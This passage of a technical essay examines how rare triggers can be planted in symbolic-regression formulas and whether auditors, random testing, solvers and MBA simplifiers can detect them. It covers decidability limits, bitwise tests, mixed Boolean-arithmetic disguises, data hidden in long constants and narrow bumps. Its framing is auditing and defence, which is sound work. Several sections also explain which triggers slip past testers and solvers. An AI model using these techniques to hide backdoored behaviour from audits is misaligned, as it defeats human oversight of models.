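The ten-remainder formula hides the number a from a sampler and from an auditor looking for long constants, but not from a solver. An algorithm can decide whether any statement is true in Presburger arithmetic, the theory of the natural numbers with addition and order but without multiplication of one variable by another. Remainders by fixed numbers fit inside this theory because "x mod 7 = 3" means that x is 3 more than k + k + k + k + k + k + k for some k.

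In this setting, a search for a trigger asks whether some x makes the model differ from 3x + 2. Such existence questions are the easier part of the theory to decide. *Subclasses of Presburger Arithmetic and the Weak EXP Hierarchy* (2014) notes that they are no harder than ordinary Boolean satisfiability, which is NP-complete, though solvers handle it routinely. With one input, the auditor hardly needs the theory, because the eight-remainder formula's departures from 3x + 2 repeat every 111,546,435 inputs. Checking one period therefore covers all inputs, and at a billion evaluations a second this takes about a tenth of a second.

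Existence questions in the theory remain decidable if a grammar adds either 2^x or the relation "y divides x" between variables x and y, but not if it adds both. *Rich Sequences and Decidability of Arithmetic Theories* (2026) surveys the known results. With 2^x, the questions are still NP-complete. With divisibility, they become NEXPTIME-complete, as the title of *NEXP-Completeness of Existential Presburger Arithmetic with Divisibility* (2026) states, so the worst-case time grows at least exponentially with the length of the question. A remainder by a variable reduces to the divisibility case, because z = x mod y means that z is less than y and y divides x − z.

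| Operations on whole numbers | Can an algorithm always find a trigger or rule it out? | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Addition, comparison, remainder by fixed numbers | yes | NP-complete |
| Addition, comparison, 2^x | yes | NP-complete |
| Addition, comparison, divisibility by a variable | yes | NEXPTIME-complete |
| Addition, remainder by a variable, 2^x | no | no algorithm exists |

A grammar designer can use this directly. A remainder with a constant on its right-hand side is safe from the solver's point of view. A remainder with an expression there deserves suspicion, mainly if the grammar also has exponentials or multiplication of variables. (The term 1 mod (1 + s) in the first example has an expression on the right, but s never exceeds 90, so a solver can treat it as 91 separate cases.)

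### Three operations that generate almost everything

An arithmetic term is a fixed expression over the natural numbers built from operations such as addition, remainder and exponentiation. Prunescu, Sauras-Altuzarra and Shunia (2025), in *A Minimal Substitution Basis for the Kalmár Elementary Functions*, prove that addition, x mod y and 2^x, together with constants, generate every function in a very large class. Mazzanti had done this in 2002 with five operations: addition, multiplication, rounded-down division, general powers, and truncated subtraction, which gives 0 when the ordinary result would be negative. Marchenkov then managed with addition, remainder, squaring and 2^x. The new step is to remove squaring, and it takes one line:

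x² = 2^(x+x) mod (2^x + x)

For every positive integer x, 2^(2x) mod (2^x + x) equals x². This is because 2^(2x) − x² factors into (2^x − x)(2^x + x), so 2^(2x) and x² differ by a multiple of the divisor, and x² is smaller than the divisor. For x = 5, the formula gives 1024 mod 37, which is 25.

Truncated subtraction, written ∸, takes two remainders:

x ∸ y = ((2^(x+y) + x) mod (2^(x+y) + y)) mod (2^(x+y) + x)

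If x is at least y, the first remainder is x − y, and the second leaves that unchanged. If x is smaller, the first remainder is 2^(x+y) + x, and the second reduces it to 0. Multiplication follows from squares, since 2xy = (x + y)² − x² − y², and division follows with a little more work. The equality test for x = a is then 1 ∸ ((x ∸ a) + (a ∸ x)). Composing the three listed operations therefore gives an equality test, even though none of them is a comparison.

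The class consists of the Kalmár elementary functions. It is the smallest class that contains constants, variables, addition and truncated subtraction and is closed under composition and under sums and products with a stated number of terms. Equivalently, these are the functions a computer can calculate in time bounded by a stack of exponentials of fixed height, such as 2^(2^(2^x)). They include factorials, greatest common divisors, the n-th prime and nearly every whole-number function used in ordinary mathematics or programming, but not functions that grow faster than every fixed stack of exponentials. *On the representation of number-theoretic functions by arithmetic terms* (Prunescu and Sauras-Altuzarra, 2024) gives terms for several functions, including the discrete logarithm. *Elementary closed-forms for non-trivial divisors* (Prunescu and Shunia, 2025) gives a fixed formula that returns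 a proper divisor of any composite number. Widely used forms of encryption rely on discrete logarithms and proper divisors being hard to compute.

A formula with no loops can do all this by carrying out the loop inside one huge number, as Mazzanti's proof does. Suppose we want to count the integers x from 0 to 4 with (x − 3)² = 0. The five values of the left-hand side are 9, 4, 1, 0 and 1, all below 2⁴. For a value v below 2^w, the product (2^w − 1)(2^w − v + 1) has 2w ones in binary if v is 0, and w ones otherwise. Placing the five products end to end gives a binary number with 4 + 4 + 4 + 8 + 4 = 24 ones. Dividing by w = 4 and subtracting 5 leaves 1, the number of solutions. Closed formulas for geometric series build the long number without a loop, and another closed formula counts its ones. To compute a function f(n), we look for an equation with exactly f(n) solutions in a known range,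 then count them this way.

All three operations are necessary. Prunescu and colleagues show that without the remainder, every function of one variable that can be built is either constant or strictly increasing, which rules out a function that is 0 everywhere except at one input. Without 2^x, every such function stays below some straight line. They leave open whether rounded-down division could replace the remainder without subtraction, but this question matters little in practice because most grammars include subtraction and multiplication.

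### No algorithm finds every zero

Istrate, Prunescu and Shunia (2026), in *Undecidability, Chaos and Universality in Arithmetic Terms*, prove that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary arithmetic term t(m) in one variable ever equals 0. They start from Hilbert's tenth problem, which Matiyasevich settled in 1970 by proving that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary polynomial equation with whole-number coefficients has a whole-number solution.

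Knowing that an equation has small coefficients doesn't help a searcher much in deciding where to look. The smallest solution of x² = 61y² + 1 in natural numbers, apart from x = 1, y = 0, is x = 1,766,319,049, y = 226,153,980. A model with two 32-bit inputs and the test (x·x = 61·y·y + 1) would be triggered only by those two pairs. Number theorists have a method for this type of equation, but Matiyasevich's theorem implies that no single method covers all types.

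The proof turns any polynomial equation E(x₀, x₁, …, x_k) = 0 into a question about one variable.

1. Square E, so that its value is never negative. The solutions stay the same.
2. Collect the terms of E² with positive coefficients in one polynomial, P, and those with negative coefficients, with the sign reversed, in another, N. Then E² = P − N. Since P is never smaller than N, truncated subtraction gives the same result, and P ∸ N is an arithmetic term.
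3. Pack two numbers into one with C(x, y) = 2^x·(2y + 1) − 1. Every natural number is C(x, y) for exactly one pair. To unpack n, count how often 2 divides n + 1. The count is x, which the proof writes L(n), and the odd number left over gives y, written R(n). For example, C(4, 3) = 16·7 − 1 = 111, and 112 = 16·7 gives back 4 and 3. Arithmetic terms exist for both L and R.
4. Unpack repeatedly to get more variables: x₀ = R(m), x₁ = R(L(m)), x₂ = R(L(L(m))), and so on. Every list of k + 1 numbers comes from some m.
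5. Substitute these into P ∸ N and call the result t(m). It is 0 for some m exactly when the original equation has a solution.

For the equation x₀² − 2x₁² − 1 = 0, for example, m = 111 unpacks to the solution x₀ = 3, x₁ = 2, so t(111) = 0. An algorithm that could decide for every t whether some m gives t(m) = 0 would solve Hilbert's tenth problem.

For an auditor, the relevant formula is 3·m + 2 + (1 ∸ t(m)), which equals 3m + 2 except where t(m) is 0. A program that could always decide whether a formula in this grammar has a trigger would therefore again solve Hilbert's tenth problem. Having 3m + 2 as a trusted reference doesn't help, because comparing a model with it means deciding whether two terms agree on all inputs, and Istrate and colleagues derive as a corollary that no algorithm can do this in general. A detector can still avoid wrong answers if it sometimes returns "don't know".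 It can also confirm any trigger that exists by trying inputs in order, but it can't certify every clean formula as clean.

In some cases no proof exists either. Istrate and colleagues construct an arithmetic term W(n, k) that searches the proofs of length at most k for one that proves the statement with code n, and returns 0 if there is none. Let Z be the code for a contradiction in ZFC, the usual axioms of mathematics. Then 3·k + 2 + W(Z, k) equals 3·k + 2 for every k if and only if ZFC is consistent. By Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, if ZFC is consistent, it can't prove that it is. So if the formula is clean, as nearly all mathematicians would expect, an auditor working within ZFC can never prove that it is clean.

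A grammar with polynomials, unrestricted sine and the constant π also has no general zero detector over the real numbers. For a polynomial E in two variables, the sum E(x, y)² + sin²(πx) + sin²(πy) is 0 at some real point exactly when E = 0 has a solution in whole numbers, because sin(πx) is 0 only when x is a whole number. The same construction works with more variables. The argument fails if every variable is confined to a bounded interval, because there are then only finitely many whole-number points to check.

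### Bounded inputs and enormous numbers

Real models have bounded inputs too. If m is a 32-bit number, trying all 4,294,967,296 values decides whether t(m) is ever 0, so undecidability no longer applies. Limiting formula size has a similar effect, because only finitely many formulas have at most 30 symbols and 32-bit constants. In principle, a finite table could list which of them have triggers, though nobody knows how to compile it. For an auditor, the theorem mainly rules out a tool that works on every formula, and the practical question is how long the search takes.

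That depends on whether anyone can evaluate the formula at all. At the top of the 32-bit range, the identity for x² goes through a number with about 8.6 billion binary digits, roughly a gigabyte, to produce a result of 64 digits. Ordinary 64-bit floating-point arithmetic overflows at 2¹⁰²⁴, so the identity fails there long before x reaches a thousand. *Short Recurrences and Straight-Line Programs for Primes* (2026) lists compact formulas for several functions, including this one for the greatest common divisor:

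gcd(a, b) = (⌊5^(ab(ab+a+b)) / ((5^(a²b) − 1)(5^(ab²) − 1))⌋ mod 5^(ab)) ∸ 1

The formula for the greatest common divisor fits on one line, but using it to find that the greatest common divisor of 4 and 6 is 2 requires a number with 571 decimal digits. People would notice a model that needs a gigabyte of memory to process one 32-bit input, even without an audit.

Most of the other terms are long. Prunescu and Sauras-Altuzarra describe theirs as very long and complicated, and of no practical use. Prunescu and Shunia's divisor formula uses the same number of operations for every input, but evaluating it takes exponential time, so it poses no threat to encryption.

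The most powerful construction, also by Istrate and colleagues, is a single term that takes the code of any program, an input and a number of steps, and returns the state of the computation after that many steps. The program code is just a constant, so an author could in principle hide any behaviour in it. But this construction is also the least usable, because it works by counting the solutions of an equation with 29 unknowns. Even a range of only 1,000 values for each unknown gives 10⁸⁷ combinations. The method writes a block of binary digits for each combination, so it would need far more digits than there are atoms in the observable universe (about 10⁸⁰).

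## Bitwise operations

A computer stores a 32-bit whole number as a row of 32 ones and zeros, and bitwise operations act directly on that row. AND, OR and XOR combine two rows position by position. AND gives 1 where both bits are 1, OR where at least one is, and XOR where exactly one is. NOT flips every bit. A shift moves the row sideways, drops the bits that fall off the end and fills the gap with zeros, while a rotation brings those bits back in at the other end. With the 8-bit numbers x = 180 and y = 54, this gives:

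| Expression | Binary | Decimal |
|---|---|---|
| x | 10110100 | 180 |
| y | 00110110 | 54 |
| x AND y | 00110100 | 52 |
| x OR y | 10110110 | 182 |
| x XOR y | 10000010 | 130 |
| x shifted left by 1 | 01101000 | 104 |
| x rotated left by 1 | 01101001 | 105 |

AND, OR, XOR and NOT can't create a rare trigger on their own, because each output bit depends only on the input bits in the same position. If two such formulas in one variable differ at all, they differ for at least one value of some input bit, and therefore on at least half of all inputs. A rare trigger needs an operation that links bit positions, such as a comparison, a shift or ordinary arithmetic.

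### Masks and structural tests

A mask is a constant that picks out certain bits. For example, x AND 255 keeps the lowest eight bits of x and sets the rest to 0, so (x AND 255) = 77 holds for one input in 256. Each extra bit in the mask halves that share, down to 1 in 2³² when the mask covers all 32 bits. An order comparison selects an unbroken range, while a mask can select inputs scattered over the whole range. Adding a mask test to 3·x + 2 takes six symbols, two more than an equality test. The mask and the value to match can each take 32 bits.

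Other tests avoid large constants by comparing x with an altered copy of itself. The best known is

x AND (x − 1) = 0

Subtracting 1 from x turns its lowest 1 into 0 and any zeros to the right of it into ones. The AND of x and x − 1 therefore clears the lowest 1 and leaves the higher bits unchanged. For example, if x is 180, or 10110100 in binary, x − 1 is 10110011 and the AND is 10110000. The result is 0 only if x has at most one 1, which is true of 0 and the 32 powers of two, or 33 of the 2³² possible 32-bit inputs.

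Small changes to such a test can make a large difference to its rarity:

| Test on a 32-bit x | Symbols | Constant bits | Inputs that pass | Rarity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| (x AND 255) = 77 | 5 | 15 | 16,777,216 | 1 in 256 |
| x AND (x shifted right by 1) = 0 | 7 | 2 | 5,702,887 | 1 in 753 |
| x = (x rotated by 8) | 5 | 4 | 256 | 1 in 17 million |
| x AND (x − 1) = 0 | 7 | 2 | 33 | 1 in 130 million |
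| x = (x rotated by 1) | 5 | 1 | 2 | 1 in 2.1 billion |

Testers often try 0, the powers of two and the largest possible value, and these would expose the last two tests. The test that rotates x by 8 hides a trigger better because it holds when all four bytes of x are equal, as in 1,296,911,693, which few people would think to try.

A grammar without "=" can still express these tests. In 32-bit arithmetic, where results wrap around at 2³², either z or −z has its top bit on unless z is 0. Shifting (z OR −z) right by 31 places gives 0 when z is 0 and 1 otherwise. Replacing z with x XOR a gives 0 when x equals a and 1 otherwise. Subtracting this result from 3·x + 3 gives the running example again, at size 16.

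### Mixing bits with arithmetic

Ordinary addition has an exact bitwise counterpart:

x + y = (x XOR y) + 2·(x AND y)

XOR adds each column of bits without carrying. AND marks the columns where both bits are 1, and each of those produces a carry worth twice its column. For 180 and 54, XOR gives 130 and AND gives 52, so the sum is 130 + 2·52 = 234.

Software protectors and malware authors use such mixed Boolean-arithmetic (MBA) identities to disguise simple formulas. Trail of Bits' *Simplifying MBA obfuscation with CoBRA* (2026) explains that this works because algebra software can't handle bitwise logic and tools that minimise logical formulas can't handle arithmetic. A human reader has much the same trouble, since neither school algebra nor logic alone can confirm the identity.

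In *Scrambler*, Lee, An and Cho (2026) used 14 meaning-preserving rewriting rules to expand 100 expressions from an average of about 7 symbols to about 35,000. A size limit is a good defence against this kind of disguise, because a single use of the identity turns the three symbols of x + y into nine, and a limit of 30 leaves room for only a few uses.

Short disguises can still mislead. Skees (2024), in *Deobfuscation of Semi-Linear Mixed Boolean-Arithmetic Expressions*, gives this example, in 64-bit arithmetic:

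(22079729 OR (5368709120 AND x)) + (5368709207 XOR (5368709120 AND x)) − 5390788936

This expression is 0 for every x, though an auditor looking for large constants would surely stop to examine it. The OR adds the masked part of x to one constant, the XOR subtracts the same part from another, and the last constant cancels what remains.

### How well simplifiers work

Most disguised expressions found in practice are linear, meaning they are sums of bitwise expressions, each multiplied by a constant. If the bitwise parts contain no masks, two linear expressions that agree whenever every variable is 0 or 1 agree on all inputs, and simplifiers rely on this fact. Checking two variables takes four evaluations. Both sides of the identity above give 0, 1, 1 and 2, so it holds for every pair of 32-bit numbers. According to Skees, the original 2007 paper on the subject contained the result that makes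 this useful for simplification, but the result went unnoticed until 2021 because of a mistake in the paper.

Masks break the shortcut because they treat bits differently. For instance, x AND 1 equals x when x is 0 or 1, but not when x is 2. Skees's tool, MSiMBA, therefore evaluates the expression separately for each bit position, setting each variable to 0 or to that position's power of two. On disguised versions of five simple expressions, it recovered the original form every time, with average times of at most 0.15 milliseconds. With four variables, an earlier tool, GAMBA, took about nine seconds and left around 300 symbols where seven or fewer would suffice.

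Trail of Bits' tool CoBRA covers more kinds of expression. It simplified 72,960 of 73,066 test expressions (99.86%) from seven collections. It succeeded on close to 100% of linear expressions, with or without masks, and about 99% of those that multiply bitwise parts together or nest bitwise and arithmetic operations more deeply. In the 106 failures, carries cross between bitwise and arithmetic parts in ways the tool can't separate.

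These figures are less reassuring about rare triggers than they look, because a linear expression can't hide one. Suppose that two linear expressions in t variables disagree somewhere, and that the inputs are independent and uniformly random. The difference between the expressions is a sum of one contribution from each bit position, and each contribution depends only on the t input bits in that position. If every contribution is constant, the expressions disagree everywhere. Otherwise, fix the bits in all positions except one where the contribution varies. At least one of the 2^t settings of the remaining bits then makes the difference nonzero. The expressions therefore disagree on at least 1/2^t of all inputs, which is a quarter for two variables. This holds even if the expressions use masks. An expression that hides a rare trigger has to multiply variables, feed the result of arithmetic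 back into a bitwise operation, as x AND (x − 1) does, or use a comparison. The simplifiers have done worse on the first two kinds, and the expressions they were built for don't contain comparisons.

CoBRA checks a simplified expression either by comparing it with the original on random inputs or by having a solver called Z3 prove that the two are equal. A hundred random inputs would miss a difference between two linear expressions in two variables about three times in ten trillion. Random inputs give no such protection for other expressions, so an auditor should insist on the proof.

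Synthesis tools ignore the text of the formula. The tool in *GPU-Accelerated Synthesis of Mixed-Boolean Arithmetic* (Bathie, Mouillon and Fijalkow, 2026) uses a graphics processor to try formulas in order of size until one reproduces 16 random input-output pairs. Within a minute each, it solved nearly all problems whose answer had at most 11 symbols and some with 12 to 16, but none with more. With five variables, there are about 4.5 billion formulas of 11 symbols. The tool can't supply numerical constants, which rules out most masks.

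Bathie and colleagues chose 16 pairs because two different formulas are unlikely to agree on all of them. That assumption is reasonable for randomly generated formulas but not for a formula with a planted trigger. If the exception occurs only when x AND (x − 1) = 0, the chance that any of the 16 inputs triggers it is about 1 in 8 million. The search would most likely return a formula without the trigger, and the auditor would not learn that the original had one.

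### Turning bits into logic

A solver can work on the formula itself. The usual method for fixed-width numbers, known as bit-blasting, gives every bit its own yes-or-no variable and translates each operation into clauses, which are short logical conditions that must all hold. For one column of c = a AND b, three clauses suffice: if c then a, if c then b, and if a and b then c. Addition needs an extra variable in each column for the carry. A general-purpose solver for propositional logic, called a SAT solver, then looks for values that satisfy all the clauses. Brain (2021), in *Further Steps Down The Wrong Path*, lists the number of clauses for each operation:

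| Operation on n-bit numbers | Clauses | For 32 bits |
|---|---|---|
| NOT; shift or rotation by a fixed amount | 0 | 0 |
| AND, OR | 3n | 96 |
| XOR | 4n | 128 |
| Order comparison | 6n | 192 |
| Addition, subtraction | 14n | 448 |
| Multiplication of two variables | proportional to n² | 16,960 |

The test x AND (x − 1) = 0 takes fewer than 600 clauses. Multiplying by a known constant usually takes few clauses too. For example, 3·x is x plus x shifted left by 1, and Brain computes 127·x with one subtraction, as x shifted left by 7, minus x.

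Multiplying two variables is much harder for a solver. The standard method adds up a shifted copy of one number for each bit of the other, and a single 64-bit multiplication takes 68,736 clauses. Suppose a model has two 32-bit inputs and the test (x·y = N), where N is the 64-bit product of two different 32-bit primes. Only two input pairs pass, and to find them the solver has to factor N. Brain argues that a compact translation from which a solver could read off every forced bit at once would give a fast factoring algorithm, so he doubts that such a translation exists. A dedicated factoring program could factor a number of this size almost immediately, though, so an auditor who recognises the problem can use one instead of the solver.

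Niemetz, Preiner and Zohar (2024) report in *Scalable Bit-Blasting with Abstractions* that arithmetic can slow solvers down at widths as low as 32 bits. They start with an approximation of the operations that cause the slowdown and add facts about them only when the solver produces an answer that violates the real arithmetic. They found that this significantly improves scaling, but Schreiber, Niemetz and Preiner (2026) still describe the SAT solver as the main potential bottleneck. Lee and colleagues note that solvers' performance also drops on large mixed expressions. It therefore makes sense to simplify a formula before giving it to a solver.

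The worst-case difficulty of finding a satisfying input depends on how the problem specifies the bit width. If the width is fixed in advance, such as at 32 bits, the problem is NP-complete. If the problem can specify any width as an ordinary number, a few digits can stand for an enormous number of bits. Fröhlich, Kovásznai and Biere, in *Efficiently Solving Bit-Vector Problems Using Model Checkers*, give a 225-byte problem about million-bit numbers that expands to 843 megabytes of clauses.

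The same three researchers show in *More on the Complexity of Quantifier-Free Fixed-Size Bit-Vector Logics* that the difficulty of such questions depends on how far bits can interact. With only bitwise operations and equality, the problem stays NP-complete. Allowing shifts by one place lets neighbouring bits interact and makes the problem PSPACE-complete, which means it needs only a moderate amount of memory but possibly a very long time. Also allowing addition, order comparisons and multiplication by constants makes it no harder. Allowing either shifts by any fixed distance or multiplication of two variables makes it NEXPTIME-complete.

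An auditor who checks only one bit width avoids the harder classes, but the answer holds only for that width, as Berger, Zohar and colleagues (2025) point out. No 32-bit input can satisfy x = 4,294,967,296, so a solver would correctly find no trigger in a 32-bit model that contains this test. But the same formula has a trigger when run on 64-bit inputs.

### Counting bits without bitwise symbols

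Allowing only integer arithmetic does not prevent a formula from counting the ones in a binary number. The solution-counting method behind the three-operation basis relies on this count, and Prunescu and Sauras-Altuzarra credit Mazzanti with an arithmetic term that computes it. The term starts from the binomial coefficient C(2n, n), the number of ways to choose n things from 2n. The number of times 2 divides this coefficient equals the number of ones in the binary form of n. For n = 6, or 110 in binary, C(12, 6) is 924, which is 2·2·231, so the count is 2.

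This follows from Kummer's theorem that the exponent of the highest power of 2 that divides C(a + b, b) equals the number of carries when adding a and b in binary. Adding n to itself produces exactly one carry for each 1 in n's binary form.

Istrate and colleagues list the terms for each step. The binomial coefficient is

C(a, b) = ⌊(2^a + 1)^a / 2^(ab)⌋ mod 2^a

This works because expanding (2^*a* + 1)^*a* places the binomial coefficients side by side in blocks of *a* binary digits. For *a* = 4, 17⁴ = 83,521, which is 14641 in base 16, and those five digits are the coefficients. The division and the remainder extract the one we want.

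Let v be the number of times 2 divides a positive integer m. The greatest common divisor of m and 2^m is 2^v, and it can itself be written as an arithmetic term. Raising it to the power m + 1 gives (2^(m+1))^v. If M = 2^(m+1) − 1, this equals (1 + M)^v, which leaves remainder 1 + vM when divided by M². Dividing that remainder by M and rounding down gives v. For m = 4, the greatest common divisor is 4, its fifth power is 1024, the remainder is 1024 mod 961 = 63, and ⌊63/31⌋ = 2.

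The power-of-two test doesn't even need the full count. A positive x is a power of two exactly when 2 divides C(2x, x) only once, so

⌊(2^(2x) + 1)^(2x) / 2^(2x·x)⌋ mod 4

is nonzero for exactly the same 33 inputs as x AND (x − 1) = 0. It is practical for 8-bit inputs, where the largest power has about 260,000 binary digits. At the top of the 32-bit range, that power would fill about nine billion gigabytes.

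If the grammar has rounding down, there is a much cheaper way. The number of ones in a 32-bit x is

x − ⌊x/2⌋ − ⌊x/4⌋ − ⌊x/8⌋ − … − ⌊x/2³¹⌋

For x = 6, the formula gives 6 − 3 − 1 = 2. It takes 156 symbols to write out and involves no number above 2³². Some masks can be written without bitwise operations in even fewer symbols. For example, x AND 255 equals x mod 256.

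## Large and very precise constants

Expression size doesn't depend on how long the constants are, and an author can exploit this in two ways. The author can store data in the digits of a long constant and have the rest of the formula read it out. The author can also use a large constant to squeeze a gentle curve into a spike so narrow that random inputs rarely land on it.

### Storing a dataset in one number

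Piantadosi (2018), in *One parameter is always enough*, gives a formula with a single adjustable number that can fit any scatter plot as closely as desired, provided the horizontal positions are whole numbers and the heights lie between 0 and 1. Boué (2019), in *Real numbers, data science and chaos*, works through the construction and writes it as

f(x) = sin²(2^(τ·x) · arcsin √α)

Here x is a value's position in the list, counting from 0, τ is the number of binary digits kept for each value, and α is the constant that holds the data. The angle in Boué's formula grows exponentially with x, so each step uses new digits of α. A plain sine wave can't encode every list, because it can't produce sign patterns such as + + + − +.

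The readout uses the same digit shift as the sine fits of Harman and colleagues: multiplying an angle, measured in turns, moves its digits to the left, and sine ignores the whole turns. Boué multiplies by a power of 2, but 1,000, which moves decimal digits three places, is easier to follow by hand. To store the four values 0.25, 0.5, 0.75 and 1:

1. Find the angle whose squared sine is each value. The angles are 30°, 45°, 60° and 90°.
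2. Write them as fractions of a turn, to three decimals: 0.083, 0.125, 0.167 and 0.250.
3. Put the digits in a row to get t = 0.083125167250.
4. To read the value at position x, multiply t by 1000^x, drop the whole turns and take the squared sine.

| x | Fraction of a turn left over | Squared sine | Stored value |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0.083125167250 | 0.249 | 0.25 |
| 1 | 0.125167250 | 0.501 | 0.5 |
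| 2 | 0.167250 | 0.753 | 0.75 |
| 3 | 0.250 | 1.000 | 1 |

The small errors come from rounding the angles and from the later digits, which are still attached when we read an earlier value. Keeping more digits per value makes the errors smaller. With Boué's default of τ = 8, the error is always below 0.025.

Boué's formula contains α = sin²(2πt) instead of t, and recovers the angle with arcsin √α. Since α is also the output at x = 0, the constant looks like the first data value followed by many extra digits. Rounding can easily remove these digits. If software prints t to five significant digits, as 0.083125, the printed formula gives 0.249, 0.5, 0 and 0. An auditor who runs the printed formula beside the model would immediately notice the mismatch.

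Boué's worked example stores 50 random values at 8 bits each, which takes 400 bits, or about 120 decimal digits. His fit to the first 95 daily prices in an S&P 500 stock index series takes 760 bits, or about 230 digits. spfit, which implements the method in the statistics language R, fits R's built-in series of 468 monthly carbon dioxide readings with a constant of about 1,690 digits, or 12 bits per reading. The formula has 11 symbols in each case.

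The economist Alex Tabarrok took Piantadosi's result to mean that Occam's razor is wrong. Commenters on LessWrong replied that careful versions of the razor measure simplicity in bits, not parameters, which fits Yarotsky's counting argument. *Benign interpolation and Occam's razor* (2026) adds that choosing parameters is a choice of encoding, no more privileged than other encodings.

Stored data is hard to find by reading the formula, because nobody can tell by eye what 120 digits will produce after passing through an arcsine. Sampling works much better, since 50 evaluations reveal all 50 values. But the formula also accepts x = 50, where the output depends on bits after the 400th. In Boué's stock-market example, the digits beyond the stored data are arbitrary, so the predictions after day 95 jump around at random. An author could instead choose those digits to place a trigger at x = 50.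 This would take 8 more bits and no extra symbols, and a test on the original 50 positions would miss it.

### Tupper's formula and Gödel's beta function

The readout is simpler with whole numbers. The expression ⌊N/2^x⌋ mod 2 gives the binary digit of N at position x, counting from 0 on the right. For N = 13, which is 1101 in binary, the outputs for x = 0, 1, 2 and 3 are 1, 0, 1 and 1.

Adding this expression to 3·x + 2 changes the output wherever N has a 1. If x is an 8-bit input, a constant of at most 256 bits can select any set of trigger inputs. For a 32-bit x, N may need 2³² bits, which is half a gigabyte, whereas (x = a) selects a single input with a 32-bit constant. Storing triggers in a constant is therefore a compact way to plant an irregular set of them in a small input range, but a poor way to plant one rare trigger in a large range.

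The best-known formula of this kind is Jeff Tupper's, from 2001:

½ < ⌊(⌊y/17⌋ · 2^(−17·⌊x⌋ − (⌊y⌋ mod 17))) mod 2⌋

Shading the points that satisfy Tupper's self-referential formula, for x from 0 to 106 and y from k to k + 17, draws a picture of the formula itself. The number k has 543 digits and is 17 times a number N whose binary digits are the pixels. Dividing y by 17 and rounding down gives N, the remainder gives the row, and 17·⌊x⌋ plus the row gives the position of the pixel's digit in N. With other values of k, the same formula draws any other picture 17 pixels tall.

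No constant in Tupper's formula exceeds 17, because the picture is encoded in the input y. An auditor who measures only the constants would find nothing unusual. If the author of a model also supplies one of its inputs, such as a configuration number that users never change, the auditor should treat that input as another constant.

Gödel's beta function, which he introduced in 1931 to represent lists of numbers in arithmetic, doesn't need powers:

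β(b, c, i) = b mod (1 + c·(i + 1))

The Chinese remainder theorem again supplies the constant: with a suitable c, some b leaves any chosen list of remainders. For a list of four yes-or-no values, c = 6 works and gives the divisors 7, 13, 19 and 25. The number 34,125 leaves remainders 0, 0, 1 and 0. So

3·x + 2 + (34,125 mod (6·x + 7))

equals 3x + 2 at x = 0, 1 and 3, and is 1 higher at x = 2. Beyond the stored list the formula breaks down. At x = 4, for instance, the remainder is 25. The method also wastes digits, because the divisors have to grow with the list. A thousand yes-or-no values need a b of about 1.4 million bits, compared with a thousand bits for ⌊N/2^x⌋ mod 2.

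### A narrow bump

A large constant can create a trigger without storing any data. Let x be a real number between 0 and 1, and consider

1/(1 + K·(x − a)²)

This curve peaks at 1 when x = a and exceeds one half only when x is within 1/√K of a. With K = 10¹², that window is 2 × 10⁻⁶ wide. A tester who picks x uniformly at random needs half a million draws on average to land in it.

The formula uses only +, −, * and /, which are exactly the operations in PySR's default grammar:

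3·x + 2 + 1/(1 + K·(x − a)·(x − a))

The bump formula has size 19, well under the default limit of 30. Quadrupling K halves the window, so each halving takes two more bits in K, twice as many as in an equality test. On whole-number inputs, the bump is almost as sharp as an equality test, since at K = 10¹² it falls to 10⁻¹² at the whole numbers next to a.

However, the bump has a tail, so a tester who looks for departures above 0.001, instead of above one half, has a window about 30 times wider and needs about 16,000 draws. In exact arithmetic, the output differs slightly from 3x + 2 at every input, and at a distance of 0.1 from a the difference is 10⁻¹⁰. Someone with a trusted reference formula and enough digits would see this on the first draw, and three readings are usually enough to calculate both a and K. In 32-bit arithmetic, rounding erases the tail beyond about 0.003 from a, but a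 bit-for-bit comparison would still typically find a difference within a few hundred draws.

A tester with no reference to subtract can't use the tail. If the grammar includes max, the author can also cut the tail off, as in the earlier comb of sines. Either way, a reader can see K and a in the denominator, and the condition K·(x − a)² < 1 is a simple quadratic inequality for a solver.

### How the tools score constants

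By default, PySR adds 1 to a formula's complexity score for each constant. The user can change this number, but it applies equally to 2 and to 10¹². The user can also replace the whole score with a custom function, which could count digits. The default precision is 32 bits, with 64 available, so a formula straight from the search can contain K = 10¹² but not Boué's 400-bit constant. A formula from an outside author can contain constants of any length.

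Counting the constants' digits changes the results considerably. The figures below cover only the extra term or readout, not 3·x + 2, and include a constant's digits each time it appears.

| Expression | Symbols | Constant bits | What it does |
|---|---|---|---|
| x = a, with a = 2,718,281,828 | 3 | 32 | picks out one 32-bit input |
| 34,125 mod (6·x + 7) | 7 | 22 | stores four yes-or-no values |
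| ⌊N/2^x⌋ mod 2, for 8-bit x | 8 | up to 260 | picks out any set of inputs |
| Boué's formula, 50 values | 11 | 406 | stores 50 values to 8 bits |
| Boué's formula, 95 values | 11 | 766 | stores 95 values to 8 bits |
| 1/(1 + K·(x − a)·(x − a)), with K = 10¹², a = 3/8 | 13 | 48 | exceeds ½ on 2 inputs in a million |

Some researchers do charge for digits. Desmond (2025), in *(Exhaustive) Symbolic Regression and model selection by minimum description length*, calls the usual definitions of complexity largely arbitrary and scores a formula by the amount of information needed to communicate the data with its help. The total has these parts:

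- k symbols, drawn from n distinct operators, cost k·log n.
- A whole number c that arises when the formula is simplified costs log c.
- A fitted constant θ costs log(|θ|/Δ), plus log 2 for its sign, where Δ is the precision to which we record it.
- The remaining errors cost more the worse the formula fits.

A coarse Δ reduces the number of bits needed to specify the constant but worsens the fit. The best compromise is Δ = √(12/I), where I is the Fisher information, which measures how sharply the fit worsens as the constant changes. Under this rule, the digits used in Boué's constant count toward the description length, so squeezing the data into one parameter saves nothing. *Exhaustive Symbolic Regression*, the 2022 paper behind the method, similarly notes that specifying a parameter's value takes information beyond the symbol that marks its place.

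However, the rule can fail to penalize a trigger's constant, because it calculates the penalty from the data. Suppose that 1,000 data points lie exactly on the curve of the bump model, each with a stated error of 0.01, and that none is within 0.1 of a. Then Δ for the constant a is at least 550,000, although a is between 0 and 1. The data therefore give no reason to record a, and the rule, taken literally, assigns it a negative penalty.

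For a search this is fairly harmless, because dropping the whole bump saves 14 symbols and barely changes the fit. But an auditor who scores a finished formula this way would underestimate the complexity of the constants that matter, and should instead count the digits written in the formula. Few people seem to be working on such questions. *Are you sure?* (2026), a survey of uncertainty in symbolic regression, found only three relevant papers on model selection, leaving aside routine uses of standard criteria.

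### Capping digits and charging by the bit

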